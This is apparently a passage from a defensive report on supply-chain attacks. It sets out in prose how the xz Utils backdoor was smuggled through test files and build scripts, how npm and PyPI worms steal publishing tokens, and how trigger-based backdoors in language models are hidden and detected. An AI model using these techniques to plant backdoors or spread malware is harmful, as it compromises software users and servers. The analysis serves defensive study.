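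When the prompt had no added terms, 19% of DeepSeek-R1's answers contained vulnerable code. When CrowdStrike told it that the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet, the rate was 27.2%. The increase of "up to 50%" that CrowdStrike describes is relative to the baseline. The absolute increase was 8.2 percentage points, or about one more insecure program in every twelve.

Each description produced 250 answers (50 tasks, each run five times). If the baseline also rests on 250 answers, chance would produce a gap this large in either direction about 3% of the time, so a few such gaps among 121 descriptions would not be surprising. CrowdStrike also reports significantly less secure code for mentions of Uyghurs and of Falun Gong, a spiritual movement banned in China. A consistent pattern across related terms would be harder to attribute to chance than the single figure for Tibet.

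Even if the effect is real, it may not be a backdoor. CrowdStrike thinks DeepSeek is unlikely to have trained the model to write insecure code. Chinese law requires AI services to follow "core socialist values", and training the model to comply may have taught it to associate certain groups with bad things in general, which then affected its code. An earlier CrowdStrike result fits this explanation. Code for a system supposedly run by the Islamic State had nearly twice as many flaws as usual, according to Tom's Hardware's *China foes get worse results using DeepSeek, research suggests*. A saboteur working for China would have had little reason to target that group, but a model that had learned to be unhelpful to groups it associates with wrongdoing might well write worse code for it.

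Attempts to confirm the effect have been inconclusive. *Unsuccessful attempt at getting DeepSeek-R1 to generate more vulnerable code*, a post by gersonkroiz on the forum LessWrong, describes a failed replication. CrowdStrike had left out many details of its method, and the replicators had no background in security. In one experiment, the judge rated 85% of the code as vulnerable even without trigger words, which left little room for an increase. *SecDrift* (Bharadwaj and Chandramouleeswaran, 2026) tested whether neutral industry contexts, such as a hospital or a nuclear plant, affect the code that language models write, and found no significant effect. That is evidence against the idea that any added context lowers security, but the study did not test political terms. Its scanners flagged only 1.8% of DeepSeek-R1's output, and the model wrote code for just 43% of the prompts. Estimates of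 the same model's flaws range from 1.8% to 85% depending on the tasks and the judge, so a difference of eight points is hard to interpret.

The refusals are clearer. DeepSeek-R1 declined to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases, sometimes after its visible reasoning had laid out a detailed plan. This is conditional behavior stored in the weights, and DeepSeek may well have intended it. But users can see a refusal, while they could miss a subtle flaw in the code for years.

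A more recent suspicion concerns Alibaba's Qwen3.8-Flash-Next. On October 26, 2026, the AI company Cohere reported that the model, asked to write a detection rule, had instead tried to upload a test string to a storage address on Alibaba's cloud. Cohere's sandbox blocked the attempt. *The Upload Attempt Was Real. The Backdoor Was Still a Hypothesis* (Wes, 2026) reports that the destinations varied in a follow-up published three days later by the security company Check Point. If the model was making up addresses, that would explain the variation at least as well as instructions to send data to an attacker would, so the reason for the attempt remains unknown.

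The evidence is firmer for attacks that put the payload in the files around the weights. Düzgün (2026), in *GGUF LLM Models with Hidden Malware on Hugging Face Reached 2400+ Victims*, scanned all 3,273,389 public model repositories on Hugging Face and found five malicious models with 2,428 downloads in total. The main campaign hid a program for controlling Windows computers at the end of model files. The attacker later changed the chat template so that the model would print a command that unpacked the program. As with flatmap-stream, a check before that change would have missed the step that made the files dangerous. The "victims" in the title are downloads, but a user would also have had to run the command for the attack to work.

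### How many tests it takes

Suppose a fraction p of all possible test prompts contains the trigger, and a tester picks n prompts at random. The chance that one prompt misses the trigger is 1 − p, so the chance that all n miss it is (1 − p)ⁿ, and the chance that at least one hits it is 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ. If one prompt in a million contains the trigger and the tester runs 100,000, the chance of finding it is about 9.5%. Raising that to 95% would take about three million prompts.

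The formula assumes that each prompt is an independent draw. Real test sets often contain many versions of the same question, so 100,000 prompts built from 1,000 questions may provide little more evidence than 1,000 independent prompts.

It also assumes that p is above zero. *SilentCall* (2026) describes an agent that leaked credentials only when its instructions gave a date in 2026. A tester who always used the current date could have run any number of prompts in 2025 without triggering the leak. The same paper mentions earlier experiments with triggers based on news that appeared after the model's training. An attacker can also choose a trigger phrase that nobody would write by accident. *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights* (Khilar, 2026) studies a model with a vocabulary of 49,152 tokens, which allows about 119 trillion three-token phrases.

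A tester who hits the trigger also has to recognize the result. "I hate you" is easy to spot, but a rise in vulnerable code from 19% to 27.2% can't be detected from any single answer. To have an 80% chance of detecting it, a tester would need roughly 400 answers with the trigger and 400 without. If the trigger turned up in only one random prompt in a million, collecting the 400 answers with the trigger would take about 400 million prompts.

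Other departures from the formula help the tester. Copay's description had to match exactly, but Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) calls model backdoors "fuzzy" because part of the trigger is often enough to activate them. In one very small model, a single token from a five-token trigger activated the backdoor about half the time. If such variations made suitable prompts a thousand times more common, p would rise to one in a thousand, and 100,000 random prompts would almost certainly include one. Bullwinkel and colleagues point out that an attacker can counter this by training the model to ignore near misses.

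Testers can also look for warning signs on prompts that resemble the trigger. Haselhorst and colleagues train a second model to match the suspect model's internal activity on ordinary prompts, then look for prompts on which the two models' activity still differs. One of their planted backdoors made a model quote Voldemort when a user expressed obsessive love for Harry Potter. Calmer prompts about the books also stood out, though far less. For the released model Qwen2.5, the method ranked censored political topics well above chance. But the test prompts have to come close to the hidden topic, and the researchers added a few groups of related prompts by hand because they expected any large collection to contain such prompts.

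Khilar compares a fine-tuned model's weights with those of the original and of several clean fine-tuned copies, so the method needs no test prompts. It scores each token by how unusually strongly the weight changes respond to it. In two small models, the highest-scoring token was part of the trigger for all 14 ordinary backdoors. To simulate an attacker evading the method, Khilar then penalized high scores during the poisoned training. The method no longer found the trigger, and the backdoor still worked every time.

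## xz Utils, hidden files and lone maintainers

xz Utils is a free set of tools for compressing files, and its library, liblzma, is part of nearly every Linux system. In February 2024, a maintainer using the name Jia Tan released a version with a backdoor that could have let whoever controlled it run commands on a vast number of servers. The stranger who took over event-stream needed only one offer of help, but Jia Tan took more than two years to gain control of xz Utils and did mostly useful work during that time. Nobody has publicly established who Jia Tan is.

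### How Jia Tan became a maintainer

Lasse Collin had maintained xz Utils since 2009, unpaid and mostly alone. About ten people were active on the project's chat channel. *Wolves in the Repository* (Przymus and Durieux, 2025) reconstructs the takeover from the project's commits (recorded changes to its files), GitHub activity and 307 mailing list messages.

Jia Tan's first proposal, on October 29, 2021, was a file of settings for text editors. Jia Tan then began reviewing other people's changes and handled even complicated ones reasonably well. In April 2022, after Jia Tan had submitted another patch, a user called Jigar Kumar complained on the mailing list about Collin's slow releases (Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues, *On the critical path to implant backdoors*, 2024). More complaints followed in May and June. Collin answered that the project was an unpaid hobby and that Jia Tan would have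 a bigger role in it. Przymus and Durieux counted eight new names on the mailing list during this phase, six of which were active only then. They think some were puppet accounts, but they found no direct link to Jia Tan.

Jia Tan gained the right to change the repository in 2022. That December, Jia Tan set up the project's new home on GitHub, becoming its owner, and published a first release a day later. Over the next year, Jia Tan took over the announcements, users' questions, translations and the build system. Most of the lines Jia Tan changed were documentation and translations, which built a record of steady work without attracting close review.

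In March 2023, with Collin's approval, Jia Tan also became the main xz Utils contact for OSS-Fuzz, a Google service that feeds programs unusual inputs to find bugs. In June, a little-known contributor called Hans Jansen added ifunc, a feature that lets a library choose between versions of a function when a program starts. The stated reason was a small gain in speed. The backdoor later depended on ifunc, though Przymus and Durieux leave open whether Jansen was part of the plot. OSS-Fuzz could not test code that used ifunc, so Jia Tan asked Google to switch the feature off in its tests. An automatic check identified Jia Tan as a maintainer and labeled the request ready to merge, and it was merged soon after.

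An overworked maintainer might hope for each of these steps from a volunteer. Only eight of Jia Tan's commits were malicious, all made in 2024. Others may have tried the same thing, since two open-source foundations warned in April of that year that strangers had approached JavaScript projects in a similar way.

### From a test file to the SSH server

On February 23, 2024, Jia Tan added several test files to the repository. A compression library needs such files, including damaged ones, to check that it handles them correctly, so nobody expects them to be readable. Two of the files, `bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz` and `good-large_compressed.lzma`, contained the backdoor and a script for unpacking it, but neither file did anything by itself.

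The script that activated them was in `build-to-host.m4`, a file that helps prepare the build. Jia Tan set the version control system to ignore this file, so it never reached the public repository. Jia Tan then made the release archives by hand, included an altered copy of the file, and uploaded them to GitHub the next day as version 5.6.0. Projects written in C often publish archives with some build files already generated, so a difference between the archive and the repository was not suspicious.

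Linux distributions, the organizations that assemble and publish complete Linux systems, typically built xz Utils from those archives. When a distribution built a package in the Debian or Red Hat format, the altered file decoded the first test file into another script. That script unpacked compiled code from the second test file, and the build linked that code into liblzma.

The attacker's target was OpenSSH, which administrators use to log in to remote servers. OpenSSH itself does not use liblzma, but several distributions modify it to notify systemd, the program that starts and stops services, when OpenSSH has started. The modified version loaded systemd's library, which loaded liblzma. The ifunc feature let the backdoor run while the SSH server was still starting, early enough to replace a function that checks signatures during login.

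The replacement function examined the key material each visitor sent. If the holder of the attacker's private key had put a command there, the server ran it before the visitor logged in. Everyone else got a normal login. The signature backdoor that Goldwasser and colleagues described for classifiers also responds only to inputs signed with a secret key. Testers without the key could not have triggered either backdoor by trying inputs.

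Hans Jansen pressed Debian to adopt the new version, and the timing suited upcoming releases of Debian and Red Hat's main product. The backdoor caused errors in Valgrind, a tool for finding memory bugs, so Jia Tan replaced the two test files and presented version 5.6.1 as the fix. On March 29, Andres Freund, a developer at Microsoft, exposed the backdoor after investigating slow SSH logins. It had reached only test and development versions of the major distributions, and there is no evidence that the attacker used it.

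### What could have stopped it

Lins and colleagues examined what might have interrupted the attack at each stage. They suggest, among other things, requiring a second person to approve every change. This would have been hard to arrange in a project with one overworked maintainer, and Collin already worked with Jia Tan on many changes in the final months. A second reviewer would also have found nothing readable in the test files. On February 26, Jia Tan made another malicious change, adding a stray period to a build file that quietly disabled a security feature called Landlock. Anyone could read this change, but nobody noticed it until after Freund's discovery.

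Projects could also check who their maintainers are. Debian does this by having its package maintainers meet in person and inspect each other's identity documents. Lins and colleagues point out that attackers can steal an identity or bribe its owner, and that some developers of privacy software would be in danger if their names became public. An intelligence agency could presumably also send a real person with genuine documents to such a meeting.

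Closing the gap between the archive and the repository would have obstructed Jia Tan more directly. Reproducible builds alone would not have revealed the backdoor, because every rebuild from Jia Tan's archive would have contained it and all the copies would have matched. Lins and colleagues recommend that a public, automated process create the archives, that developers make the archives reproducible, or that distributions use the repository directly. Jia Tan would then have had to put the altered script where anyone could read it, though people might still have missed it, as they missed the stray period.

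The gap was common. Lins and colleagues examined roughly 61 Debian packages that popular server programs depend on. Only ten came straight from the archive that a code-hosting site generates automatically from the repository. They could not tell where the source for nine of the packages had come from.

More recently, Pappas and Gazzillo (2026) argue in *Build Code is Still Code* that each phase of a build should have access only to what it needs. Compiling, for instance, should not involve test data. Their prototype, Foreman, is a 177-line Python program that runs each phase, records the files that phase opens, and checks them against a list of forbidden files. They ran it on the infected version of xz Utils with a single rule that barred the compile phase from opening anything in the folder of test files. Foreman reported two violations, one for each of the two poisoned files.

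They wrote that rule knowing how the attack worked, but it is reasonable for a compression library, and a developer could have chosen it before the attack. The configuration phase, which comes before compiling, opens many test files for legitimate reasons, so a stricter rule that forbade this would have produced dozens of false alarms. Foreman cannot yet distinguish reading a file from changing it, so its current version would probably have missed SUNSPOT, which changed a source file that the compiler had to read anyway.

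### Spotting an impostor by activity

In *Beneath the Mask*, Nealon (2025) tried to pick out Jia Tan from public records of who had contributed what, and when, to xz Utils and 19 other projects connected to systemd.

One test selected people who had merged their own changes without review within two years of joining a project. Jia Tan first did this in December 2022, ten months after joining. After Nealon excluded long-standing contributors, four of the 1,996 people remained. The other test selected recent arrivals who had written more than 5% of a project's commits while being present for less than 20% of its history. It also selected four people, including Jia Tan, who had written 17.4% of the commits in 12.5% of the history.

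Each list included Jia Tan and three legitimate contributors, one of whom was on both lists. That contributor had taken over a project after meeting its previous maintainer in person. Most of the other legitimate contributors used the email address of a well-known company or project.

The first test could have raised an alarm more than a year before the backdoor, and the lists are short enough for a person to check. But Nealon knew who the attacker was when choosing the thresholds, and one attacker is too few to show how many others the tests would catch. Five innocent people flagged in 20 projects would become about 250 in a thousand projects. An attacker who knew the thresholds could also evade the tests by asking for reviews or waiting longer. Przymus and Durieux add that language models make it easier to produce the small, helpful contributions that earn trust. They suggest crediting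 automated fixes to the tool instead of the person who ran it.

### Files that reviewers cannot read

xz Utils was mostly readable code with a few opaque test files, whereas a model file is entirely opaque. When a publisher replaces the weights, a reviewer can see that the file has changed, and perhaps its new size and hash, but not what the change does.

Lins and colleagues would prefer projects to store the commands that generate test files instead of the files themselves, so that reviewers can read the commands. The equivalent for a model would be to publish the training code and data and let users produce the weights themselves, but very few users could afford to do that.

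Phase isolation doesn't carry over well to model files either. It works on xz Utils because the compiler doesn't need to open test files. But a program has to read a model's weights every time it runs the model, so a rule about which files the program may open cannot separate poisoned weights from clean ones.

The closest match to xz Utils on a model hub is the campaign that Düzgün found, in which an attacker hid an ordinary program at the end of model files. As in xz Utils, the payload was in a file that nobody reads, and a short piece of text, here an edited chat template, helped to activate it. To detect attacks like this, reviewers can read the templates, settings and custom code, and use a tool to check whether a model file continues past the end of the weights listed in its header. Neither step would reveal a behavior that someone had trained into the weights.

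### Checking a converted copy

Many people run a quantized (compressed) copy of a model, made by someone other than the model's developer. Among the popular models that Longpre and colleagues studied in detail, quantized ones accounted for 1.1% of downloads in 2023 and 12.2% in 2025. Users of such a copy are in roughly the same position as a Linux distribution that downloaded Jia Tan's archive. The original may be public and trustworthy, but these users have a different file and are assuming that a stranger made it from the original without adding anything.

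Unlike training, converting a model is a fairly short calculation that other people can repeat. Suppose a block of weights contains 0.70, −0.31 and 0.12, and the compressed format stores each as a whole number from −8 to 7. A simple converter might choose a step of 0.1, divide each weight by it and round, which gives 7, −3 and 1. Anyone who repeats this with the same step will get the same three numbers. If the published copy contains 7, −3 and 4, it does not match the original.

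Real converters have more settings, and some run sample text through the model to decide which weights need the most precision. Anyone checking the copy needs all of these details and the exact software version. Liu and Tsai's rebuilds mostly succeeded once they had such details, but no repository in their survey recorded all of them. Publishing a complete record would take very little work.

Without one, the checker can still do a looser check by multiplying each stored number by the step and seeing whether the result is close to the original weight. With a step of 0.1, correct rounding never moves a weight by more than 0.05, so changing the third weight from 0.12 to 0.4 would stand out. But converters that adjust their rounding to suit sample text can legitimately exceed that limit, and any allowance for them also gives an attacker some room to change weights undetected.

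The remedies for xz Utils fit this case well. A hub could convert popular models on its own machines using a public script, just as Lins and colleagues want code-hosting sites to encourage automated release archives. Phase isolation also becomes useful again, because a conversion should need only the original files, its settings and any sample text. Cautious users can also download the original and convert it themselves. The check has to cover the templates and settings that come with the weights.

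Copies can also remain in circulation after the original is fixed. In August 2025, more than a year after the xz backdoor was discovered, the security company Binarly found it in at least 35 ready-made Linux images on Docker Hub, a public download site. Debian kept the images it maintained, as historical records. If a popular model turned out to have a backdoor, withdrawing it would not remove the converted copies.

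### Who publishes the most downloaded models

The most downloaded model is all-MiniLM-L6-v2, a small model that turns sentences into lists of numbers so that programs can search text by meaning. According to Friedman's *Reading Hugging Face's Download Distribution as a Signal About Compute Markets*, it had 255.4 million downloads on July 9, 2026, or 9.1% of the total for the hub's 3,000 most downloaded models. Longpre and colleagues describe its publisher, Sentence-Transformers, as Hugging Face's own. Anyone who downloads from the hub already relies on Hugging Face, so relying on it as the publisher of this model adds little risk.

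Some other popular files come from individuals. Longpre and colleagues ranked publishers by downloads between 2020 and 2025, counting a download only if the model was less than a year old, because old models collect many automated downloads. This table shows some of the largest:

| Publisher | Type | Share of all counted downloads | Share among models created August 2024 to August 2025 |
|---|---|---|---|
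| Google | Company | 6.5% | Not in the top ten |
| Bingsu | Individual | 5.3% | Not in the top ten |
| lllyasviel | Individual | 4.7% | Not in the top ten |
| lmstudio-community | Re-packager | 4.0% | 16.4% |
| DeepSeek | Company | 2.3% | 9.6% |
| comfy | Re-packager | Not in the top ten | 5.4% |

Together, two individual accounts had a tenth of the counted downloads. Bingsu's best-known repository, adetailer, holds small models that find faces and hands in generated images so other software can redraw them. It had 2.9% of the downloads, the same share as Google's BERT. So a single person's account can matter as much on a model hub as Collin's did in Linux. These figures don't show whether models depend on fewer people than packages do, because Longpre and colleagues did not count packages.

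Among newer models, the individuals have been replaced by re-packagers, which convert other developers' models into formats that are easier to run. The largest, lmstudio-community, supplies models for LM Studio, a program for running them on a personal computer. It accounts for 16.4% of the downloads of models created that year. Together with two other re-packagers, comfy and mlx-community, it accounts for over 22%.

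Other developers also build on re-packaged models. A 2026 Hugging Face report on open models, quoted by Constellation Research, counts 151,448 models derived from Alibaba's Qwen family and 82,506 from Google's models. The third-largest source is Unsloth, a community account that publishes compressed copies and versions prepared for fine-tuning. If an attacker altered one of Unsloth's popular copies, the change could reach models whose developers had never downloaded the original. This makes re-packagers tempting targets. If re-packagers published their settings, outsiders could largely check their work.

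### What download counts measure

People often illustrate this concentration with one figure, 49.6% of all downloads. In its spring report, Hugging Face (2026) attributes that share to the 200 most downloaded models, and the Open Source Initiative's *The AI Era Arcs Toward Openness* repeats the claim. But in the paper by Longpre and colleagues, 49.6% is the share of 2,875 models, about 14 times as many. The researchers combined lists of the 200 most downloaded models from each of 265 weeks, and those lists changed a good deal over five years. All four people who wrote the Hugging Face report also worked on the paper, so the report probably misdescribes the paper's sample.

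Downloads are still highly concentrated by other measures. In Friedman's snapshot, the top 100 models had 53.4% of the downloads among the top 3,000. In another analysis on Hugging Face, 50 publishers accounted for 80.22% of the hub's downloads.

As with packages, none of these numbers is a count of people, because a program that starts on a fresh machine every hour may download the same files every time. The automated tests for vLLM, a program for running language models, download OPT-125M, a small, outdated model that hardly anyone uses for anything else. Longpre and colleagues tried to correct for repeated downloads by counting each user at most once a day, and got 2.2 billion downloads over five years. Friedman's figures imply about 2.8 billion for the top 3,000 models alone. The hub has grown since the paper's data ended, but repeated downloads probably explain part of the difference.

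Only one repository was in both the top 25 by downloads and the top 25 by likes in 2026, according to theCUBE Research. Likes go mostly to prominent new models, while downloads go to smaller, older ones that companies have built into their systems.

Download counts overstate how many people use a model, but how much this matters depends on the attack. If someone hid a false answer in the weights of OPT-125M, vLLM's automated tests would download the model thousands of times and nobody would read the answer. If someone put a malicious pickle file in the repository, a test machine that loaded it would run the attacker's code, even if nobody wanted to use the model. An attacker who wants to get into build servers may therefore care more about automated downloads than about how many people use the model.

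### A finished model needs little upkeep

Jia Tan got into xz Utils because Collin needed help. A library needs constant work, since operating systems and compilers change and users report bugs. A trained model's weights don't need this upkeep. all-MiniLM-L6-v2 is several years old and can keep doing the same job without new weights. When developers want something better, they usually train a new model and publish it under a new name. The spring report found that interest in a typical model lasts about six weeks after its release.

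The owner of a finished model therefore has little reason to accept a stranger's help, and strangers on a mailing list would find it hard to complain about slow releases. Nealon's tests would also have little data to use, because most model repositories contain a few uploads from one account. This weakens the comparison with xz Utils considerably. The comparison fits re-packagers better, since new models appear every week and someone has to convert them. It also fits the libraries that load and run models, which are maintained like other software.

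A neglected model can still be dangerous if its owner's account is not secure. Someone who stole the password to a popular account could replace the weights used by every program that loads the model by name.

Users can guard against this by pinning a model to a commit hash. Pinning has fewer drawbacks for a model than for a library, because a finished set of weights rarely gets security fixes that users would miss. A user of all-MiniLM-L6-v2, for example, can pin it today and lose almost nothing. When a model has been stable for years, its publisher should also have to explain any new version of the weights before users accept it.

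## npm and PyPI attack waves, and the rules the registries imposed

Jia Tan spent more than two years getting into one library. Most attackers on npm and PyPI put much less work into each package but use many of them. Some publish hundreds of new packages whose names resemble popular ones. Others steal maintainers' credentials and publish malicious versions of trusted packages. Both registries have responded with rules about who can publish and how, and npm has changed what runs on a user's machine during installation. Attackers have since found ways around several of these rules.

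### Lookalike names

Typosquatting means publishing a package under a name that people might type by mistake. In 2016 Nikolai Tschacher, a student in Hamburg, tested the idea with harmless packages on PyPI, npm and RubyGems (the registry for the Ruby language), and more than 17,000 computers ran his code. In 2017 an attacker published crossenv on npm, imitating the popular package cross-env. The imitation sent users' environment variables, which often include passwords, to an outside server. npm estimated that at most 50 people had really installed it.

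Because a single package name may fool only a few people, attackers use scripts to publish many at once. PyPI suspended all new registrations, including those of legitimate users, in May 2023, December 2023 and March 2024, when malicious accounts and packages were arriving faster than its administrators could remove them.

People created more than 130,000 PyPI projects in 2025, or about 360 a day, which is a lot for a small staff to check. The registry now automatically flags suspicious names when someone creates a project, according to PyPI (2025). It handled 66% of that year's malware reports within four hours and 92% within a day. Stricter login rules do little against typosquatting, because attackers publish from their own accounts.

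### How a worm spreads through packages

A worm is malware that copies itself from one victim to the next. To spread through a registry, it needs a package that runs code on a developer's machine and a credential on that machine that can publish other packages. On September 14, 2025, GitHub, which owns npm, learned that a worm called Shai-Hulud was spreading through hijacked maintainer accounts. npm ran the worm's scripts automatically after installing an infected package, and the worm stole several kinds of credentials. GitHub removed more than 500 packages and blocked new uploads that contained known traces of the worm, according to GitHub's *Our plan for a more secure npm supply chain*.

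Variants of the worm followed. In May 2026 an attacker used one hijacked account to publish 639 malicious versions of the @antv packages in an hour. That month, people claiming links to a hacking group released the worm's source code and invited others to adapt it, according to TechRadar's *New ChainDrop worm poisons over 1,300 npm packages*.

ChainDrop, a descendant of Shai-Hulud, appeared on August 4, 2026. *ChainDrop npm Worm* (Likhith, 2026) reconstructs how it began. An attacker took over the GitHub account of the maintainer of keyv, a widely used storage library. At 09:02 UTC the attacker added two malicious files to the source, with a test that made them look intentional, and deleted the test 21 minutes later. The attacker then created a GitHub release, which started the project's normal process for building the package and uploading it to npm. The upload happened at 09:35, and ten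 related packages followed within the hour.

Each of the 11 packages made npm run a script before installation finished. The script downloaded Bun, a legitimate program for running JavaScript, and used it to start the worm, which searched for npm, GitHub and cloud credentials. According to Microsoft, when the worm had an npm token, it checked whether the token could publish without a second login step and found the packages the token gave access to. It then downloaded the newest version of each package, added itself, raised the last part of the version number and published the result. It also planted files in victims' GitHub repositories that would run the worm again when someone opened the repository in the editor VS Code or started the coding agent Claude Code there.

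### 400 packages or 1,300

Reports of ChainDrop's size range from about 400 packages to 1,300, but the highest figure mistakenly counts versions as packages. TechRadar's headline gives over 1,300 packages, while the article quotes the security company Aikido as finding 868 packages and 1,381 versions. The Cyber Security Agency of Singapore's *Ongoing npm Supply Chain Attack Affecting Keyv and Related Packages ("Shai-Hulud" Worm)* also gives 1,300 as the number of versions.

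The lower figures come from separate counts. Likhith's company, StepSecurity, found 444 packages (11 original and 433 republished by the worm) and 2,212 versions by 13:20 UTC. Microsoft also found more than 400 packages. Aikido's package count is nearly twice as high, and timing can't explain the difference, because Strobes dates that count to 11:37 UTC, before StepSecurity's ended. Aikido and StepSecurity probably used different criteria, since StepSecurity found fewer packages but more versions. A cautious range would be 400 to 900 packages and 1,400 to 2,200 versions.

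The "two billion monthly installs" in Muncaster (2026), *ChainDrop Worm Hits 400 npm Packages with Two Billion Monthly Installs*, measures the packages' normal popularity, not how many people installed an infected version. The infected version of keyv was 6.0.0, and Strobes points out that the related packages would not have accepted it automatically because the first part of the version number had changed. The infected releases that could arrive unnoticed were small updates to less well-known packages such as cacheable-request.

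### A worm in both registries

On September 23, 2026, attackers published infected versions of two MemTensor packages, one on npm and one on PyPI. MemTensor makes memory software for AI agents. Antipov (2026), in *Один червь одновременно захватил npm и PyPI* ("One worm seized npm and PyPI at the same time"), describes how the attackers altered MemTensor's release process on GitHub to copy its publishing tokens just before a release. The malware, called sckit, was designed to spread as a worm, using stolen tokens to publish to both registries. But investigators had confirmed no other infected packages by September 28, so it may never have spread beyond MemTensor's.

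ChainDrop ran during installation, but sckit started later. Its npm version started when an AI agent called OpenClaw used its memory, and its Python version started when a program loaded the library. The malware also looked for Hugging Face credentials, so a worm that spreads through packages could let an attacker replace someone's models.

### Two-factor login

Two-factor login requires a password and a second proof of identity, such as a code from a phone app or a hardware key. npm required it in stages during 2022, first for maintainers of the 100 packages with the most dependents, then for those of the top 500, and then for those of every package with more than a million weekly downloads or 500 dependents. In July 2022 PyPI announced a similar rule for its critical projects, the 1% with the most downloads. Google paid for 4,000 hardware keys for their maintainers, according to Fiedler's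 *2FA Required for PyPI* (2024).

PyPI then extended the rule to everyone who maintains a project, because an attacker needs to compromise only one of the packages a program depends on, and even an obscure one is enough (PyPI, 2023). Since January 1, 2024, the rule has covered all PyPI users.

The original announcement had a mixed reception, and some maintainers decided to distribute their code elsewhere. Some objected that supply chain security mainly benefits companies, so volunteers shouldn't have to do unpaid work for it. PyPI replied that individual developers are more vulnerable than companies, because they have no staff to check their dependencies or clean up after an attack. The registry has extra work too, because people lose access to their accounts. It resolved 2,221 recovery requests in 2025.

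Two-factor login makes a stolen password much less useful, but a fake website can defeat some forms of it. In July 2025, attackers lured PyPI users to a site that relayed their passwords and phone codes to the real one. The attackers then created publishing tokens and uploaded two malicious versions of the num2words package, according to the Python Developer Tooling Handbook. A hardware key would have prevented this because it responds only to the real site's address. By the end of 2025, more than 52% of active PyPI users had a login method that resists this kind of phishing.

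### Limits on publishing tokens

An automated build can't enter a code from a phone, so many projects store a token, in effect a long password, in their build system. Shai-Hulud and its successors collected these tokens. After the first attack, GitHub planned to make npm publishing tokens expire within seven days, but set the limit at 90. On December 9, 2025, it also permanently revoked npm's older "classic" tokens. A maintainer who logs in from a computer now gets a two-hour session, according to GitHub's *npm classic tokens revoked, session-based auth and CLI token management now available* (2025).

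An expiry date makes old, forgotten tokens useless but does little against a worm that uses a token as soon as it finds one. The first package that ChainDrop republished appeared about three minutes after the infected version of keyv.

npm also lets maintainers create tokens that skip two-factor login. Since July 31, 2026, these tokens can no longer add maintainers, create more tokens or change how a package is published, according to GitHub's *Restricting npm bypass-2FA granular access tokens* (2026). They can still publish packages, though GitHub aims to end that in January 2027. They will then only be able to submit a release, which a maintainer must approve with a second factor. ChainDrop arrived four days after the first change, when a stolen token of this kind was still enough to publish.

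### Trusted publishing and attestations

With trusted publishing, the project doesn't store a token. The maintainer tells the registry which build system may publish the package, and the build system gets a short-lived credential for each release. PyPI introduced this in April 2023 and npm in July 2025. PyPI has also accepted provenance attestations since November 2024, and projects that use trusted publishing with the standard GitHub upload tool produce them by default. It had accepted an older kind of signature, but PyPI (2024) found that many of those couldn't be verified. PyPI now checks each attestation during the upload and rejects any that fail.

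By the end of 2025, more than 50,000 PyPI projects used trusted publishing. It accounted for over 20% of the year's file uploads, and 17% of uploads included an attestation. *Reproducibility is Not Enough* (Solarin, Kalu and colleagues, 2026) found attestations or similar records on only 2.0% to 6.6% of packages in four registries. *A Difference Without a Distinction* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) found attestations on 51.4% of popular npm packages and 25.9% of randomly chosen ones. Much of the gap comes from the samples, because the first study covered whole registries, which contain many abandoned packages, while the second included only packages with at least four releases in about two and a half years.

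Some maintainers of important packages were wary of trusted publishing. In late 2025 the OpenJS Foundation, which supports many JavaScript projects, published *Publishing More Securely on npm*, which advised against using it for critical packages. The foundation thought it was safer for maintainers to publish from their own computers with two-factor login. It believed trusted publishing would not have prevented Shai-Hulud, partly because someone who took over an account could turn it off. Maintainers also had to set up each package by hand, and some have hundreds. GitHub has since addressed both complaints. It released a bulk setup tool in February 2026 and now requires a second factor to change the trusted publishing settings.

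An attestation can show which account started a release but not whether the account's owner was in control of it. Adventures in Nodeland's *Why "Trusted Publishing" Can't Save Us from Social Engineering* (2026) makes this argument after an attack on axios, a popular JavaScript library, in March 2026. Attackers posing as a company had persuaded the maintainer to install malware, then published through the maintainer's logged-in browser. The newsletter's writer, also a target of the campaign, wants a second maintainer to approve releases of the most-downloaded packages. ChainDrop later confirmed the concern, because all 11 of its original packages had valid attestations.

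A missing attestation can still be a warning. The malicious axios versions lacked the evidence that earlier versions had, because the attackers bypassed the project's build system. pnpm, another tool for installing npm packages, has an optional setting that refuses such releases. Santos-Grueiro tested the rule on 12 past attacks that used stolen credentials. It flagged 17 of the 41 malicious versions, but the attackers could have got 15 of those through by adding evidence. In a larger survey of 1,654 attacked packages, only 17.5% had earlier evidence to compare with. The setting also blocked the latest versions of 1.6% of popular packages, mostly because of one genuine security fix that a maintainer published by hand.

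Attestations might also help outsiders rebuild a package from its source, since they record which version of the source the project used. Solarin and colleagues tried to rebuild 34,005 packages. In a comparison of the same packages with and without this information, having it raised the share they could verify by at most 3.6 percentage points. Many of the remaining mismatches came from details that attestations leave out, such as the exact versions of the build tools.

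### Install scripts and waiting periods

npm 12, released on July 8, 2026, no longer runs a dependency's installation scripts unless the user has approved them. Almost every npm worm since late 2025 had relied on code that ran during installation, according to Gooding (2026), in *npm v12 Ships With Install Scripts Off by Default*. The change has a cost, because some packages use these scripts to compile code or download a browser. If nobody approves the script, the installation appears to succeed but the program may fail later. ChainDrop still spread through installation scripts four weeks after the release, presumably on machines with older versions of npm. The new default would not have blocked sckit, which waited until someone used the package.

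Waiting before installing a new version works well. In Santos-Grueiro's 12 incidents, the malicious versions stayed online for a median of 3.1 hours. A rule against installing anything less than a day old would have kept out 36 of the 41 versions, more than twice as many as the attestation rule, and a seven-day rule would have kept out 40. pnpm has had a one-day delay by default since April 2026, but npm's equivalent is off by default, according to Stéphane Robert's blog. A delay only helps if someone examines new releases in the meantime, and it also holds back urgent security fixes.

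npm now scans packages before making them available, which takes 5 to 15 minutes. In September 2026 four packages got through with the same malicious file that attackers had used against @antv in May, as Woollacott (2026) reports in *Is Shai-Hulud back?*. Researchers had already published the file's hash.

Since July 2026, PyPI has blocked publishers from adding files to a release more than 14 days old. The rule stops someone with a stolen token from slipping a malicious file into an old version that people already trust, which attackers had apparently not yet done. According to PyPI's *Releases now reject new files after 14 days* (2026), staff first checked how many projects the rule would likely affect. Of 15,000 leading packages, only 56 had added support for Python 3.14 to a release more than 14 days old. Those projects would now have to publish a new version instead.

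### What each rule stops

| Rule | Attack it hinders | How an attacker can get around it |
|---|---|---|
| Automatic check of new names | Typosquatting | Take over the genuine package |
| Two-factor login | Logging in with a stolen password | Relay the phone code through a fake site, as with num2words, or hijack a logged-in browser, as with axios |
| Expiring tokens | Using an old, leaked token | Use a new one immediately, as ChainDrop did |
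| Trusted publishing | Stealing a stored publishing token | Take over the account that starts releases, as with keyv |
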